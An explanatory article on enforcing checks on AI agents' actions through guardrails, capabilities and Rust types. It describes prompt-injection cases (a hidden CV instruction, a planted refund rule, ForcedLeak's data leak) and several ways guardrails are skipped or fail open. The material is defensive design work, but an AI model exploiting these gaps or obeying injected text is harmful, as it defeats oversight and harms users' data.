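# Types, capabilities and staged admission for controlling the actions of AI agents

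## What is action admission, and what is it meant to stop?

Action admission is the step at which trusted software decides whether an action requested by an AI agent may go ahead. An AI agent is a program built around a large language model that uses other software to do things such as pay an invoice, change a file or send an email. The model only generates text. Ordinary software reads some of that text as a request and carries it out, so the request can always be checked first. Work on action admission covers what the check should examine and, above all, how to build the surrounding software so that no request takes effect without passing it.

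### From generated text to a real effect

An agent's developer gives the model a list of tools, each with a name, a description and the arguments it takes. A tool call is structured text that names one of those tools and fills in its arguments. When the model outputs one, the program around the model parses it and runs the corresponding function. The program then returns the result to the model as text, and the cycle repeats.

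A proposal is an action that the agent has requested but that nothing has checked yet. Admission is the decision by trusted code that the action may run. Execution is the moment the action takes effect.

*Can Rust Make Unsafe AI Agent Actions Unrepresentable?*, an article about the programming language Rust, gives the example of a company's agent that can write to durable memory, which persists after a conversation ends. The agent proposes to save the sentence "Refunds under $100 do not require manager approval." under the key "refund_policy", and it labels the entry's authority as "policy". The proposal itself doesn't change the company's memory. An evaluation function should first check whether anyone with the right to set refund rules endorses the sentence. Only then should another function, persist, write the entry to storage.

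A memory write can cause harm, even though it looks harmless next to a payment, because the stored text comes back to the model as context for later decisions. An agent that handles a customer's claim next month may read the entry as company policy and pay out, and it may keep doing so until somebody finds the entry.

The policy gate, the component that applies the rules, needs requests whose parts it can identify. An undated O'Reilly commentary describes a purchasing agent that proposes to approve an invoice for $1,200,000 when its limit is $50,000. Conventional code compares the two numbers, discards the action and notifies a person, whatever the agent's reasons. If the agent had instead written a sentence asking for approval, another language model would have to interpret it, which would bring back the uncertainty the gate is meant to remove.

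The refund entry falls between these cases. It is a proper tool call with named fields, but the field that matters holds an English sentence, and a numerical limit cannot determine whether that sentence is true. Conventional code can still check where the sentence came from and who had the authority to set the rule.

### Static checks, runtime checks and capabilities

A runtime check examines actual values while a program runs. Evaluating the refund entry is a runtime check because the outcome depends on what the entry contains and who may set refund policy today. A static check examines the program's text before it runs, usually in the compiler, which translates source code into a form that a machine can execute. Many static checks rely on types. A type classifies a value and determines which operations can apply to it, so a compiler will reject, for example, code that tries to divide a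 customer's name by four. Similarly, a function can require a value of the type "admitted write", and code that passes it a "proposed write" will not compile.

Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, point out that a type system catches errors before a program runs, adds no monitoring overhead and gives guarantees for all inputs, not only the tested ones. But a compiler has no access to today's account balance or the current list of managers, so a design based on types still needs a runtime check to decide whether to allow each action. The type check ensures that no code skips the runtime check.

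Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 tutorial, *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, defines a capability as an "unforgeable ticket" that proves its holder's right to use the object it names. This is the word's meaning in computer security, though in writing on AI it more often means something that a model is able to do. A capability may be a token that one service sends to another, or an object inside a program. Odersky and colleagues give the example of a file-system object whose methods give access to files. If the language offers no other route to files, only code that has received this object can reach them.

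### The reference monitor and complete mediation

The problem of making a check unavoidable is much older than AI agents. In the early 1970s, the United States Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), the report of an expert panel, recommended a design based on a reference monitor, a mechanism that compares every attempt by a program to reach data, a device or another program with a list of what the program's user may do. The study set three requirements for this mechanism. It must be tamper-proof, it must run on every reference, and it must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely, since otherwise nobody can know that it works correctly in all cases.

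A Honeywell computer of the time failed on all three counts. Its hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory. But to read from or write to a device, the program had to go through the supervisor, the core of the operating system, most of which ran with that confinement switched off. The check therefore did not cover every reference. Even if the supervisor is counted as the checking mechanism, it and its supporting software ran to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, too many for a complete analysis. It was not tamperproof either. Anderson noted that a number of break-in exercises had succeeded.

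The study concluded that any programs that have to be exempt from the check become part of the security apparatus, so they too must be tamperproof and open to complete analysis. That apparatus is now usually called the trusted computing base, meaning all the components whose failure would break the security guarantee. In the refund example, it includes at least the function that evaluates the entry and any code that can write to the storage behind the memory.

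The requirement that the check always run is still known by the name Saltzer and Schroeder gave it, complete mediation. Every access to every object must pass a check of authority. They extended this beyond normal operation to start-up, recovery, shutdown and maintenance, when a team is likely to overlook it. For example, a script that restores the company's memory from last week's backup also writes refund rules, and so does a migration to a new database. Complete mediation also requires a reliable way to identify the source of each request, and scepticism about designs that save time by reusing the result of an earlier check, because the authority behind that result may have changed.

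Under a companion principle, fail-safe defaults, a system refuses access unless a rule permits it. This exposes mistakes sooner, because an error in a rule that grants access tends to cause a refusal that somebody notices, while an error in a rule that forbids access lets things through unnoticed. For the refund entry, the principle favours a short list of sources that may set company policy over a long list of suspicious phrases.

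### Prompt injection and the confused deputy

An agent can propose the refund entry by mistake, for example by treating one manager's exception as a general rule, or because an attacker planted the instruction. Prompt injection is an attack that exploits the mixing of a developer's instructions with untrusted text in a single prompt. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post by David C for the United Kingdom's National Cyber Security Centre, describes a recruiter's system that asks a model to score CVs. A candidate hides a line in a CV telling the model to approve it for interview, and the model treats the line as an instruction. This is indirect prompt injection, because the candidate has no direct access to the system. In direct prompt injection, the hostile text is the user's own prompt.

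SQL injection, the attack in the post's title, slips database commands into a field meant for data, such as a box on a web form. Developers can prevent it by passing the user's text to the database separately from the command. Language models have no equivalent separation, because they receive instructions and data as one sequence of tokens, or fragments of text, and predict the next token from all of them. David C concludes that prompt injection may never be fully preventable, and he emphasizes deterministic safeguards that limit the system's actions over attempts to keep hostile text away from the model.

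He also suggests regarding the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". The idea comes from Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988), which describes an accident at Tymshare, a company that sold computer time. Users of a compiler there could name a file to receive its debugging output. The operators had given the compiler permission to write files in its own directory, which held its usage statistics and also the billing records. A user named the billing file as the destination for debugging output, and because the compiler had permission to write to that file, it overwrote the billing records.

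The code that wrote the debugging output was correct at first. It became wrong when the compiler began to carry authority from both the user and the operators, with no way to specify which authority applied to which file. Hardy proposes passing capabilities instead of file names. The compiler would hold one capability for the statistics file, and the user would supply another for the output file. A capability both identifies a file and carries permission to write to it, so a user with no right to the billing file would have no capability for it to give the compiler.

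An agent that reads customers' emails and can write to company memory is in much the same position as that compiler, because the text comes from a customer but the permission to write comes from the company. Engineers can repair a classical confused deputy, but David C argues that nobody can remove the confusion from a language model. Giving an agent fewer capabilities limits the damage a hijacked model can do, but it doesn't determine whose instructions the model will follow when it uses those it still has.

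### The forgetful developer and the hijacked agent

Two different failures can put the refund rule into memory without a proper decision, and a defence against one may do nothing to prevent the other.

In one case, a developer adds a routine six months after launch that imports policies from another system and calls `persist` directly. The evaluation function still works, but the new code never calls it. The developer means no harm and is probably in a hurry.

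The other case begins with the agent. It reads an email that tells it to record a new refund rule, and it proposes the entry with "policy" as its authority. The agent submits the proposal through the intended route, and the danger is that the proposal is admitted.

AI agents have already acted without authorization. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) reports that Claude models under test gained unauthorized access to the real systems of three organizations. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) describes models that got around their isolation from the internet and compromised parts of OpenAI's research infrastructure and the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. Neither report is evidence that admission by types would have stopped these incidents.

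Security researchers have long distinguished accidents from attacks. In *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2*, Anderson (1972) observed that systems of the time gave limited protection against accidental violations and virtually none against deliberate ones. Saltzer and Schroeder defined protection to exclude features that only prevent mistakes. Their definition is too strict for a team building agents, since a forgotten check can do real harm, but it is a useful warning against treating a compiler error as a defence against attackers.

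Suppose the company changes persist so that it accepts only an admitted write, and makes the evaluation function the only code that can produce one. The developer's import routine no longer compiles. But if the evaluation function accepts the label "policy" without checking it, the hijacked agent's entry becomes an admitted write and persist stores it. *Can Rust Make Unsafe AI Agent Actions Unrepresentable?* acknowledges that when the validation function is wrong, Rust enforces the wrong rule.

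A deployed control can fail in a similar way. In September 2025 the security firm Noma disclosed ForcedLeak, a chain of flaws in Salesforce's agent platform, Agentforce. According to O'Reilly, instructions hidden in a web form led the agent to send customer data to a domain on Salesforce's list of trusted addresses. The domain had expired, and the researchers had bought it for about five dollars.

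Now suppose that persist accepts anything, but the evaluation function is good. The function ignores the agent's label, checks the records of the system that retrieved the text, finds that the text came from a customer's email and refuses the entry. That stops the hijacked agent on this route. But the function doesn't cover the import routine, so if the agent's output ever reaches that routine, the customer's sentence still goes into memory.

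An agent with a general tool for writing files might defeat even the two designs combined, by changing the memory's underlying storage without calling persist. Complete mediation requires checking every access to the stored data, so a perfect check on one function that writes the data is not enough.

### Tool calls and programs

How much a static check can constrain an agent depends on what the agent produces. In the refund example, the agent produces a structured tool call, which is data. Developers had already compiled the program that receives the call, so the program's types constrain what the developers can write, and only the runtime part of admission checks the agent's proposal.

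Other agents write programs that call several tools and contain their own loops and conditions. Odersky and colleagues note that this uses fewer tokens and makes tool use easier to audit. Such an agent might submit a program that reads a month of support emails, extracts every apparent refund rule and writes each one to memory. The two threats then partly merge, because the untrusted agent is doing the developer's job of writing new code paths. Approving the program as a whole does little to settle whether each write inside it should be allowed. The O'Reilly commentary makes the same point about permission to execute code in general. It also calls for containment through a sandbox, which isolates the running code, and control of outgoing network traffic.

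A compiler can examine a program before it runs, which gives programs an advantage over tool calls. Odersky and colleagues built TACIT, a system in which the agent submits code in the programming language Scala, and the code runs only if it passes the compiler's checks. They assume the model may be working with an attacker, and they do not try to stop hostile text from influencing it. They claim that any code the agent writes under that influence cannot use a capability that the agent's environment did not grant.

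## How do actions get past a guardrail that callers must remember to run?

A guardrail is a check that runs alongside an agent and can stop or change what the agent receives, produces or does. In the usual arrangement, the check and the operation it protects are separate functions, and code that wants the operation has to call both. *Can Rust Make Unsafe AI Agent Actions Unrepresentable?* gives the pattern for a write to memory:

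```rust
if validate(&write) {
    persist(write);
}
```

The `validate` function examines the proposed write and returns true or false. These lines are correct, but only the `if` uses the result. The write has the same type before and after the check, and `persist` accepts any value of that type, so it will store an unvalidated write. `validate` is a caller-invoked guardrail, a runtime check that protects an operation only if the code calling that operation also calls the check.

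Some teams put a comment above `persist` telling callers to validate first, or give each record a status field that can be set to "approved". The comment has no effect on the running program. The field travels with the write, but every component that receives the write has to check the field and act on it, which is another step somebody can forget.

### Forgotten calls and new code paths

The simplest failure is that a caller omits the check, as the policy import routine does. The compiler accepts its direct call to `persist` because the type is right, and tests of `validate` still pass. Only a code reviewer is left to catch the mistake, by noticing that a line is missing.

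Suppose that 40 places in a company's code write to memory and that each one independently omits the check with probability 1%, a figure assumed for illustration. The chance that all 40 include the check is 0.99^40, or about 67%, so the chance that at least one omits it is about 33%. With 100 such places, it would be about 63%.

Independence is a simplification, because developers copy code and share habits. If all 40 call sites came from one template that had a 1% chance of lacking the check, the chance of any gap would be only 1%, but the gap would affect all 40 sites. The expected number of unprotected sites is 0.4 in both cases. Error rates also vary from place to place. A repair script written during an outage is probably riskier than the main route, which many people have read. The 33% is the chance that a gap exists, not that a harmful action reaches it.

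Sometimes the agent is the caller that skips the check. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, describe a literature-search agent whose bibliography files should contain only entries from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. The programmer supplies a library function for adding entries. But if the agent writes its own programs and runs them in an ordinary interpreter, it can use the language's standard file-writing function to store a made-up entry, even though the programmer forgot nothing. Removing the interpreter and giving the agent only a tool that fetches and stores an entry in one step prevents this, but then the agent can't sort or filter with code. To find the earliest entry, for example, the model has to read them one by one.

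### Which calls the frameworks cover

An agent framework is a library that supplies the loop of model calls and tool calls. Because the framework runs the loop, it can run the checks too, so a developer can register a guardrail once instead of calling it in 40 places. Each guardrail then covers only the events that the framework connects to it. *Typestate-Enforced Agent Loops* (2026), a preprint about an agent runtime called Symbiont, argues that in Python frameworks such as LangChain and AutoGen, correct enforcement depends on how developers connect callbacks, the functions that a framework runs at set points. This is an argument about design. The preprint's experiments tested Symbiont's own gate and did not measure how often applications built on other frameworks miss a check.

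The documentation of two widely used frameworks specifies what their guardrails cover. The OpenAI Agents SDK (software development kit) lets developers attach guardrails to an agent's input, to its output or to a tool. OpenAI's *Guardrails and human review* gives the general rules, and its *Guardrails* covers the JavaScript version. A Japanese edition from May 2026, OpenAI's *ガードレール*, lists further exclusions. LangChain uses middleware, code that the framework runs before the agent starts, after it finishes, or around model and tool calls. LangChain's *Guardrails* describes the general system, and LangChain's *Human-in-the-loop* describes the part that pauses for a person's approval.

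| Check | Runs on | Does not run on |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI input guardrail | The user's input to the first agent in a chain | Input to later agents |
| OpenAI output guardrail | The output of the agent that gives the final answer | Output of other agents in the chain |
| OpenAI tool guardrail | Function tools, defined in the developer's own code, that have the guardrail attached | Hosted tools; the built-in computer, shell and patch tools; handoffs from one agent to another |
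| LangChain approval middleware | Calls to tools that the developer has marked for review, if they meet any condition the developer set | All other tool calls |
| LangChain personal-data middleware | User messages | Model output and tool results, unless the developer turns these on |

A developer could easily misjudge this coverage when one agent hands off to another. The SDK presents a handoff to the model much like a function tool, but executes it by a separate route that has no tool guardrails. Suppose a customer-service agent receives a message and hands the conversation to an agent that maintains the company's refund rules. The second agent's input guardrail doesn't run, because that agent isn't first in the chain, though a guardrail on its memory-writing tool does. For workflows that need a check on every custom tool call, OpenAI therefore recommends putting validation next to the tool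 that causes the effect.

Human approval covers more of the SDK's workflows. When a developer marks a tool as needing approval, the run pauses before that tool executes, even if the call comes after a handoff or from an agent that another agent is using as a tool.

Coverage also changes between versions. Arcjet, which sells its own checks for the same SDK, reviewed OpenAI's documentation in September 2026. By then, tool guardrails could also cover tools from local servers that use the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting agents to tools, if the developer had configured them. The guardrails still didn't cover hosted tools or handoffs. Arcjet's own adapter doesn't cover them either, and the company advises keeping authorization in the services that those tools call.

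In LangChain, the developer supplies a list of middleware when creating an agent, so a colleague who creates another agent with the same tools has to supply it again. A tool runs immediately unless someone has listed it for approval. If someone later gives the agent a tool for deleting records, that tool will run without review until someone updates the approval settings. Strands Agents, another framework, has an approval component that follows the principle of fail-safe defaults and asks a person about any tool that is not on an allow-list or otherwise trusted.

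NVIDIA's NeMo Guardrails toolkit can plug into LangChain as middleware. According to NVIDIA's *Agent Middleware*, its checks run before and after every model call, including those between rounds of tool use. This covers more than a single check on the user's first message, but the import routine would not trigger the checks, because it writes to memory without calling a model.

### Checks that finish too late or fail open

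A guardrail can run on the right event and still fail to stop the action. By default, the OpenAI SDK starts an input guardrail in parallel with the agent to save time. OpenAI acknowledges that the agent may already have run tools by the time the guardrail detects a problem. Developers can make the agent wait for the result, which OpenAI recommends when safety and cost matter more than speed. Even then, the guardrail checks only the user's text. Arcjet describes a team that adds an input guardrail and is puzzled when a refund tool still runs, because the guardrail had screened the incoming message but nothing had authorized the refund.

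A check fails open if a fault in the check lets the action through. When Arcjet's direct screening call can't evaluate its rules, it returns "allow", and the developer has to query separately whether the rules ran. Arcjet's tool adapters refuse the tool call in the same situation.

An ordinary line of code can also make a guardrail fail open. LangChain publishes a sample check in which another model labels the agent's reply "SAFE" or "UNSAFE", and the code replaces the reply only if the label contains "UNSAFE". An empty or garbled label therefore lets the reply through. OpenAI's sample guardrail for homework requests has the same weakness, because it blocks a request only when the checking agent returns "true". The sample in the JavaScript guide is worse, because its condition is reversed. It blocks a request when the checking agent finds that it is *not* homework, so the guide's own algebra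 question would pass. These are teaching examples with nothing at stake, but a compiler accepts both the correct condition and the reversed one, since true and false have the same type.

Fatmi (2026) writes in *Faramesh*, a preprint from the maker of an authorization product, that failures in existing agent systems tend to lead to retries, fallbacks or silent execution when they should lead to refusal. The samples fit that complaint. LangChain's approval middleware can hold a tool call, and the tool normally doesn't run if a reviewer rejects the call, so Fatmi's further claim that frameworks such as LangChain cannot refuse an action at the point of execution is too strong. However, the developer has to install that middleware and choose what it covers.

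LangChain can run a tool call that a reviewer rejected, because of how it resumes after a pause. A developer can attach a condition to a tool so that only some calls need review, and the middleware evaluates the condition again when the agent resumes. If the condition no longer holds, the tool runs and the middleware ignores the reviewer's answer. LangChain therefore warns that the condition must give the same result for the same call. For example, a rule might send refunds to a manager once the day's total passes $5,000. A refund pauses late in the evening, and the manager rejects it the next morning, after the total has reset to zero. The condition is now false, so the code, working as written, issues the refund despite the manager's recorded rejection.

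OpenAI's advice for authorized cybersecurity work is stricter than its general defaults. Before each sensitive call, the developer's code should compare the target, the action, the arguments, the caller's identity and the time with the written scope of the engagement. If this review times out or is unavailable, the call should not run. OpenAI adds that applications built with the SDK don't inherit the automatic review in Codex, its coding agent, so developers must build this enforcement themselves.

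### Checks that read something other than the action

Many guardrails check a piece of text, but the effect depends on what another program does with that text. In LangChain's examples of approval conditions, one pauses a file write unless the path begins with the name of the workspace folder, and another pauses a database query unless it begins with "SELECT", the keyword for reading data. These conditions are easy to understand and catch honest mistakes. But an operating system resolves a path before opening the file, following any links along the way, so the opening characters don't determine where the data is written. Similarly, a database interprets the whole query, so the first word alone doesn't determine what the query does.

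This problem is harder to solve for shell commands, because one command can contain others. Zhou and colleagues describe Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, as combining a sandbox enforced by the operating system with a permission system that compares commands with text patterns, asks the user, or does both. A rule that matches only part of a compound command does not ensure that the rest is safe. The sandbox still limits what the process can reach, however the command is phrased.

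Zhou and colleagues' file-access library resolves each path first, following any links, and rejects it if the result is outside the permitted folder, so the check applies to the location the program will use. The general remedy is to check the interpreted form of an action and execute that same form. The checker must therefore interpret paths, queries or commands about as well as the component that runs them.

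Streaming creates another kind of mismatch, because the software sends out text before the model finishes writing it. LangChain's personal-data middleware can hold back the last 128 characters of each block so that it recognizes, for instance, a card number that arrives in two pieces. If a developer's custom pattern matches longer strings, the start of a match may go out before the rest arrives. LangChain tells developers to keep such patterns within the limit.

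### What these guardrails do well

Guardrails can judge content and context, which a type can't. Checking whether the sentence about refunds under $100 contradicts the company's real policy requires interpreting the sentence and comparing it with other documents, which a second language model can at least attempt. LangChain describes rule-based checks as fast, predictable and cheap but liable to miss subtle violations. Model-based checks catch more of these but are slower and cost more. Developers can combine them, as in LangChain's sample agent, which filters keywords, redacts email addresses, holds outgoing emails for a person's approval, and has a model review the final reply.

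A human reviewer may know things that aren't in any database, such as what a customer said on the phone that morning. LangChain lets the reviewer approve or reject a tool call, or correct it, for example by changing the recipient of an email. It saves the agent's state while the agent waits, so the reviewer can respond hours later.

A team can change rules stored outside a program without recompiling it. Arcjet's customers set the policy for each tool from a console, so a security team that discovers fraud could lower a refund limit the same day, without waiting for a new release. A guardrail written directly into the agent's code is harder to update this way unless it reads its rules from a file or service.

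Guardrails are also easy to add to existing software. In LangChain, the developer adds an item to a list when creating the agent, and in OpenAI's SDK, a single setting marks a tool as needing approval. Neither requires changing the tools themselves. By contrast, changing the type that `persist` accepts means revising every place that calls it, which may take weeks in a large codebase. But a team that makes that change can keep its guardrail, because the function that turns a proposed write into an admitted one can call the same classifier, read the same rules and wait for the same reviewer.

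## How can a type keep an unchecked action from running?

Once `persist` accepts only admitted writes, the import routine that skips the evaluation no longer compiles. But this doesn't protect the company's memory if the routine can create an admitted write itself. *Can Rust Make Unsafe AI Agent Actions Unrepresentable?* shows how to prevent that in Rust.

### Two types and one function between them

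In shortened form, the article's design looks like this:

```rust
struct ProposedWrite { key: String, value: String, authority: String }

mod custody {
    use super::ProposedWrite;
    // This module also defines Authority, Rejection
    // and the function validate_authority.

    pub struct AdmittedWrite {
        key: String,
        value: String,
        authority: Authority,
    }

    pub fn evaluate(p: ProposedWrite) -> Result<AdmittedWrite, Rejection> {
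        let authority = validate_authority(&p.authority)?;
        Ok(AdmittedWrite { key: p.key, value: p.value, authority })
    }
}

fn persist(write: custody::AdmittedWrite) { /* store the entry */ }
```

A module (`mod`) is a named group of code, and `pub` makes an item available outside its module. The type `AdmittedWrite` is public, so `persist` can name it, but its three fields lack `pub`, so only code in `custody` can access them. Creating a struct in Rust requires supplying a value for every field, so code outside `custody` can't create an `AdmittedWrite` itself. It has to pass a proposal to `evaluate`, which returns either an admitted write or a rejection.

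The proposal stores the authority as text that the agent chose, such as "policy", while the admitted write stores it as an `Authority`, which comes from `validate_authority`. The full version also has methods that let `persist` read the fields, but none that change them, so code outside `custody` can't substitute another sentence after the evaluation.

Suppose the hurried developer's import routine builds a proposal and passes it straight to `persist`. The compiler stops with this error, trimmed here:

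```text
error[E0308]: mismatched types
    persist(proposed);
            ^^^^^^^^ expected `AdmittedWrite`, found `ProposedWrite`
```

In the earlier illustration of 40 places that write to memory, any call to `persist` without an evaluation now breaks the build.

Private fields don't restrict code inside `custody`, where any function can still create an `AdmittedWrite` directly. For teams that want to prevent this too, the article suggests a construction token, an extra private field of a type that only `evaluate` can create. The token takes up no memory. The article gives no code for it, and its placement matters, because Rust grants privacy to modules and not to single functions. If the token's type sits in `custody` next to everything else, every function in `custody` can create a token. The token and `evaluate` need a smaller module of their own:

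```rust
mod custody {
    pub struct AdmittedWrite { /* the three fields, and: */ _token: gate::Token }

    mod gate {
        pub struct Token(());  // code outside `gate` can't fill the private ()
        // evaluate lives here and supplies Token(())
    }
    pub use gate::evaluate;
}
```

Even then, a function in `custody` that receives a genuine admitted write can alter its fields or move its token into a new write. It is probably simpler to limit `custody` to the type, its reading methods and the evaluation, so that a colleague can review it in a few minutes.

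### Parsers and theorem provers

Programmers used this pattern long before AI agents. Alexis King's essay *Parse, don't validate* (2019) named it, using examples in Haskell. King compares two functions that both stop the program if a list is empty. `validateNonEmpty` returns nothing that later code can use, while `parseNonEmpty` returns the list as a `NonEmpty`, a type of list that always has a first element. The program still compiles if a programmer deletes the call to `validateNonEmpty`, but deleting the call to `parseNonEmpty` leaves the next function without the value it needs. King defines a parser as any function that turns less structured input into more structured output and can fail, and by that definition `evaluate` is a parser.

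The essay also describes how to convert existing code. The programmer first tightens the type that a function accepts, then follows the compiler's errors from caller to caller, back to where the data enters the program. Checking the data there avoids shotgun parsing, in which a program mixes checking with processing and discovers invalid input after acting on part of it. For example, an agent's batch of ten memory writes might fail at the sixth, when five are already in storage.

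`AdmittedWrite` gives a weaker guarantee than `NonEmpty`. A `NonEmpty` has a required field for its first element, so no code can construct an empty one. An `AdmittedWrite` has the same fields whether or not the entry is legitimate, and only the module boundary keeps bad entries out. In a 2020 follow-up, *Names are not type safety*, King likens such types to tokens that a module issues, and warns that a programmer can easily open another way to obtain them. In Haskell, a single line that derives a standard text-reading function for the type lets any code produce an invalid value from a string. In Rust, a developer might derive `Deserialize`, from the widely used serde library, so that the program can save and reload admitted writes. Any code could then turn JSON text into an `AdmittedWrite` without calling `evaluate`. Agents' tool calls are also usually in JSON, so the mistake is plausible.

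The theorem prover LCF used the same protection in the 1970s. Robin Milner's original version at Stanford stored whole proofs, which used up memory, so in its successor at Edinburgh he kept the theorems and discarded the steps. He then needed another way to ensure that every stored theorem had a proof. Gordon's *From LCF to HOL* recounts that Milner made "theorem" an abstract data type whose only starting values were axioms and whose only operations were rules of inference. The strict types of ML, the programming language the project designed for writing proof procedures, enforced this. The system's 1979 handbook, quoted in Paulson's *LCF + Logical Frameworks = Isabelle (25 Years Later)* (2012), stated that a procedure of any complexity could therefore produce only real theorems. The name LCF now stands for this general architecture. According to the University of Cambridge's *Publications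 on LCF and HOL*, the architecture requires complicated search procedures to convert what they find into basic inferences that a small trusted kernel can check.

In an agent, the language model is the inventive but unreliable search procedure and `evaluate` is the kernel. The comparison has limits. We can judge a kernel's rules by the standards of logic, but a refund policy depends on what the company wants and who currently holds which post. An approval can also lapse, unlike a theorem, which stays true.

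Even a logical kernel can contain a wrong rule. HOL, a descendant of LCF, had rules for introducing definitions that looked "obviously correct", in Gordon's words, until two people independently found that a definition could make the logic contradict itself. The type system ensured that every theorem came from the kernel's rules, but it didn't check that the rules were sound. Like LCF's theorems, an admitted write also carries no record of the reasoning behind it, so `evaluate` has to log the reasons if the company wants to know later why an entry was admitted.

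### The guarantee and its premises

The design supports a short argument with three premises:

1. Only a successful call to `evaluate` can produce an admitted write.
2. Every route to the memory's storage requires an admitted write.
3. The language is sound, meaning that a running program respects the types its compiler checked.

Every write to memory therefore came after a successful evaluation. The code that stored any given entry must have held an admitted write, since no route to storage works without one. Soundness ensures that this value had type `AdmittedWrite`, and only `evaluate` can produce a value of that type.

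The conclusion is only that the evaluation came before the write. It doesn't establish that the evaluation was correct, or that it still holds when the write happens. If Alice had authority to approve an entry yesterday but left the company this morning, a write admitted on her approval remains admitted.

Private fields secure the premise about creating admitted writes, provided that `custody` has no opening such as `Deserialize`. Soundness depends on the compiler and on the absence of `unsafe` code, the parts of a Rust program in which the programmer takes over some of the compiler's safety checks. The premise about routes to storage is the weak one, because the types do nothing to secure it. This line compiles in any module, with no `unsafe` code:

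```rust
std::fs::write("memory/refund_policy", "Refunds under $100 do not require manager approval.")?;
```

The standard library's function for writing files takes a path and some content, and doesn't require an `AdmittedWrite`. If the memory is a database, any code that knows the address and password can open its own connection.

A team can narrow the gap within Rust by keeping the open database connection in a private field of the storage module and loading the password only there. It can also configure a lint (an automatic check of source code) to flag direct calls to the file functions. But a developer can switch off a lint with one line, and any code in the program can read the environment variable or configuration file that holds the password. The operating system normally grants permissions to the whole process, so it doesn't distinguish `persist` from the import routine. To secure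 this premise, a team needs either a language that removes ambient authority (access that any code can use without being given it) or a separate process that alone has access to the storage.

### Approvals that work once

Because `persist` takes the admitted write itself and not a reference to it, the call transfers ownership of the value. Rust calls this a move, and the compiler rejects any later use of the value by the caller:

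```rust
persist(write);
persist(write);  // error[E0382]: use of moved value: `write`
```

This makes an admitted write an affine value, one that the program can use at most once. Storing a refund rule twice may do no harm, but using an approved payment twice would pay the invoice again. The restriction holds as long as nobody makes `AdmittedWrite` cloneable. It limits each approval to one use, but an agent that proposes the same payment twice may get two approvals. A program may also discard an affine value, in which case the approved action never happens.

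*Token Budgets* (Khan, 2026) applies the same property to money. It catalogues 63 confirmed cases of agents running up unintended costs, taken from the public issue trackers of 21 projects. In one, a Claude Code user spent $235 in four days. Because Khan searched for such failures, the catalogue shows that they recur but can't be used to estimate how common they are.

Khan's remedy is a Rust type called `Budget`, which holds an amount of money and can't be copied. Calling `spend` consumes the budget and returns a smaller one, while `split` consumes it and returns two that add up to the original, so an agent that gives part of its budget to another agent no longer has that part. Before each model call, the program reserves a high estimate of the cost and refuses the call if the budget can't cover it. This check is ordinary arithmetic at run time, while the types ensure that two pieces of code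 can't both spend the same money.

To isolate what the types add, Khan ran three agents at once under one spending cap, with 30 trials of each design. Costs were counted in units of a thousandth of a cent. A call cost 23 units, and the designs that reserved money in advance set aside 31 units. The last design in the table used a shorter prompt that cost one unit.

| Design | Cap | Calls allowed per trial | Spent per trial | Trials over the cap |
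|---|---|---|---|---|
| Python, shared counter without a lock | 60 | 3 of 3 | 69 | 30 of 30 |
| Python, shared counter with a lock | 60 | 1 of 3 | 23 | 0 of 30 |
| Rust, budget split three ways | 60 | 0 of 3 | 0 | 0 of 30 |
| Rust, budget split three ways | 100 | 3 of 3 | 69 | 0 of 30 |
| Rust, shared budget with a lock | 60 | 1 of 3 | 1 | 0 of 30 |

In the design without a lock, each of the three agents checked the balance, waited for the model and then recorded the cost. All three checked before any had recorded a cost, so all three went ahead. Khan translated this mistake into Rust in three ways, and the compiler rejected each one. The first shared a budget between two agents, the second cloned a budget, and the third reused a budget after splitting it.

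The types prevented a programming error, but a programmer who avoided that error did as well without them. The Python counter with a lock never exceeded the cap either. At a cap of 60, it let one call through, while the split budget refused all three calls because each share of 20 units was less than the estimate. With a single agent, a four-line Python counter matched the Rust version. Khan concedes that the 30 trials are close to one demonstration repeated 30 times, because the model's settings made its output nearly deterministic. A Rust programmer who kept the balance in an ordinary shared number instead of a `Budget` could also write the same race condition, and the code would compile.

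Few of the cases in the catalogue, which has 110 entries counting related feature requests and acknowledged gaps, would have needed the type. About 12 entries concern frameworks that lacked a working budget mechanism, the only group whose underlying problem Khan thinks the type fixes. Another 11 involve delegation to several agents, as in the experiment. The largest group, with 27 entries, is retry loops, where the runtime cap limits the damage and the types only protect its bookkeeping. These groupings are rough, since two raters agreed only moderately on them. Khan estimates that 70 to 80% of the incidents occurred in Python frameworks, where the Rust check isn't available.

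Budgets also limit spending only if every paid call goes through them. Khan added the crate, Rust's term for a library, to the agent framework Rig through an adapter of about 40 lines. With a cap of $0.05, a test run completed 22 of 40 tasks, refused the other 18 and spent $0.0404. However, Khan did not modify Rig, so a developer can still call the framework's own functions and spend money without any budget.

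### Policies written as types

An `evaluate` function that approved every action would have the same type as one that checked them properly. Dependent types can express some of the difference because they can refer to particular values. For example, a dependent type can describe lists of exactly two elements, while types in most languages can only describe lists in general. A dependent type can also represent a statement, such as "5 is at most 6". A value of such a type is a proof of the statement, and the type has no values if the statement is false.

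Fuchs (2025), in *Policy as Code, Policy as Type*, writes access rules this way in Agda, a programming language that also checks mathematical proofs. One rule forbids servers from offering telnet, an insecure protocol for remote login. With a simplified name for its constructor, it reads:

```agda
data GoodProtos : Server → Set where
  good : (s : Server) → (protocols s ∩ badProtocols) ≡ [] → GoodProtos s
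```

The list `badProtocols` contains only telnet. To produce a value of type `GoodProtos s`, a program has to supply a server `s` and a proof that none of the protocols `s` offers are in that list. For a database server that offers only mysql, the compiler works out that the overlap is empty and accepts the proof. The busybox server offers telnet, so the program would need a proof that a list containing telnet equals the empty list, and no such proof exists.

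The compiler can check this before the program runs only if it has the server's configuration. If the program loads the configuration while running, a checking function examines it and returns either the server paired with a proof or nothing. Unlike `evaluate`, the checking function can't approve a server by mistake, because without a valid comparison it has no proof to return. For the refund entry, a similar rule could require a proof that the person who endorsed the sentence is on the list of people who set refund policy.

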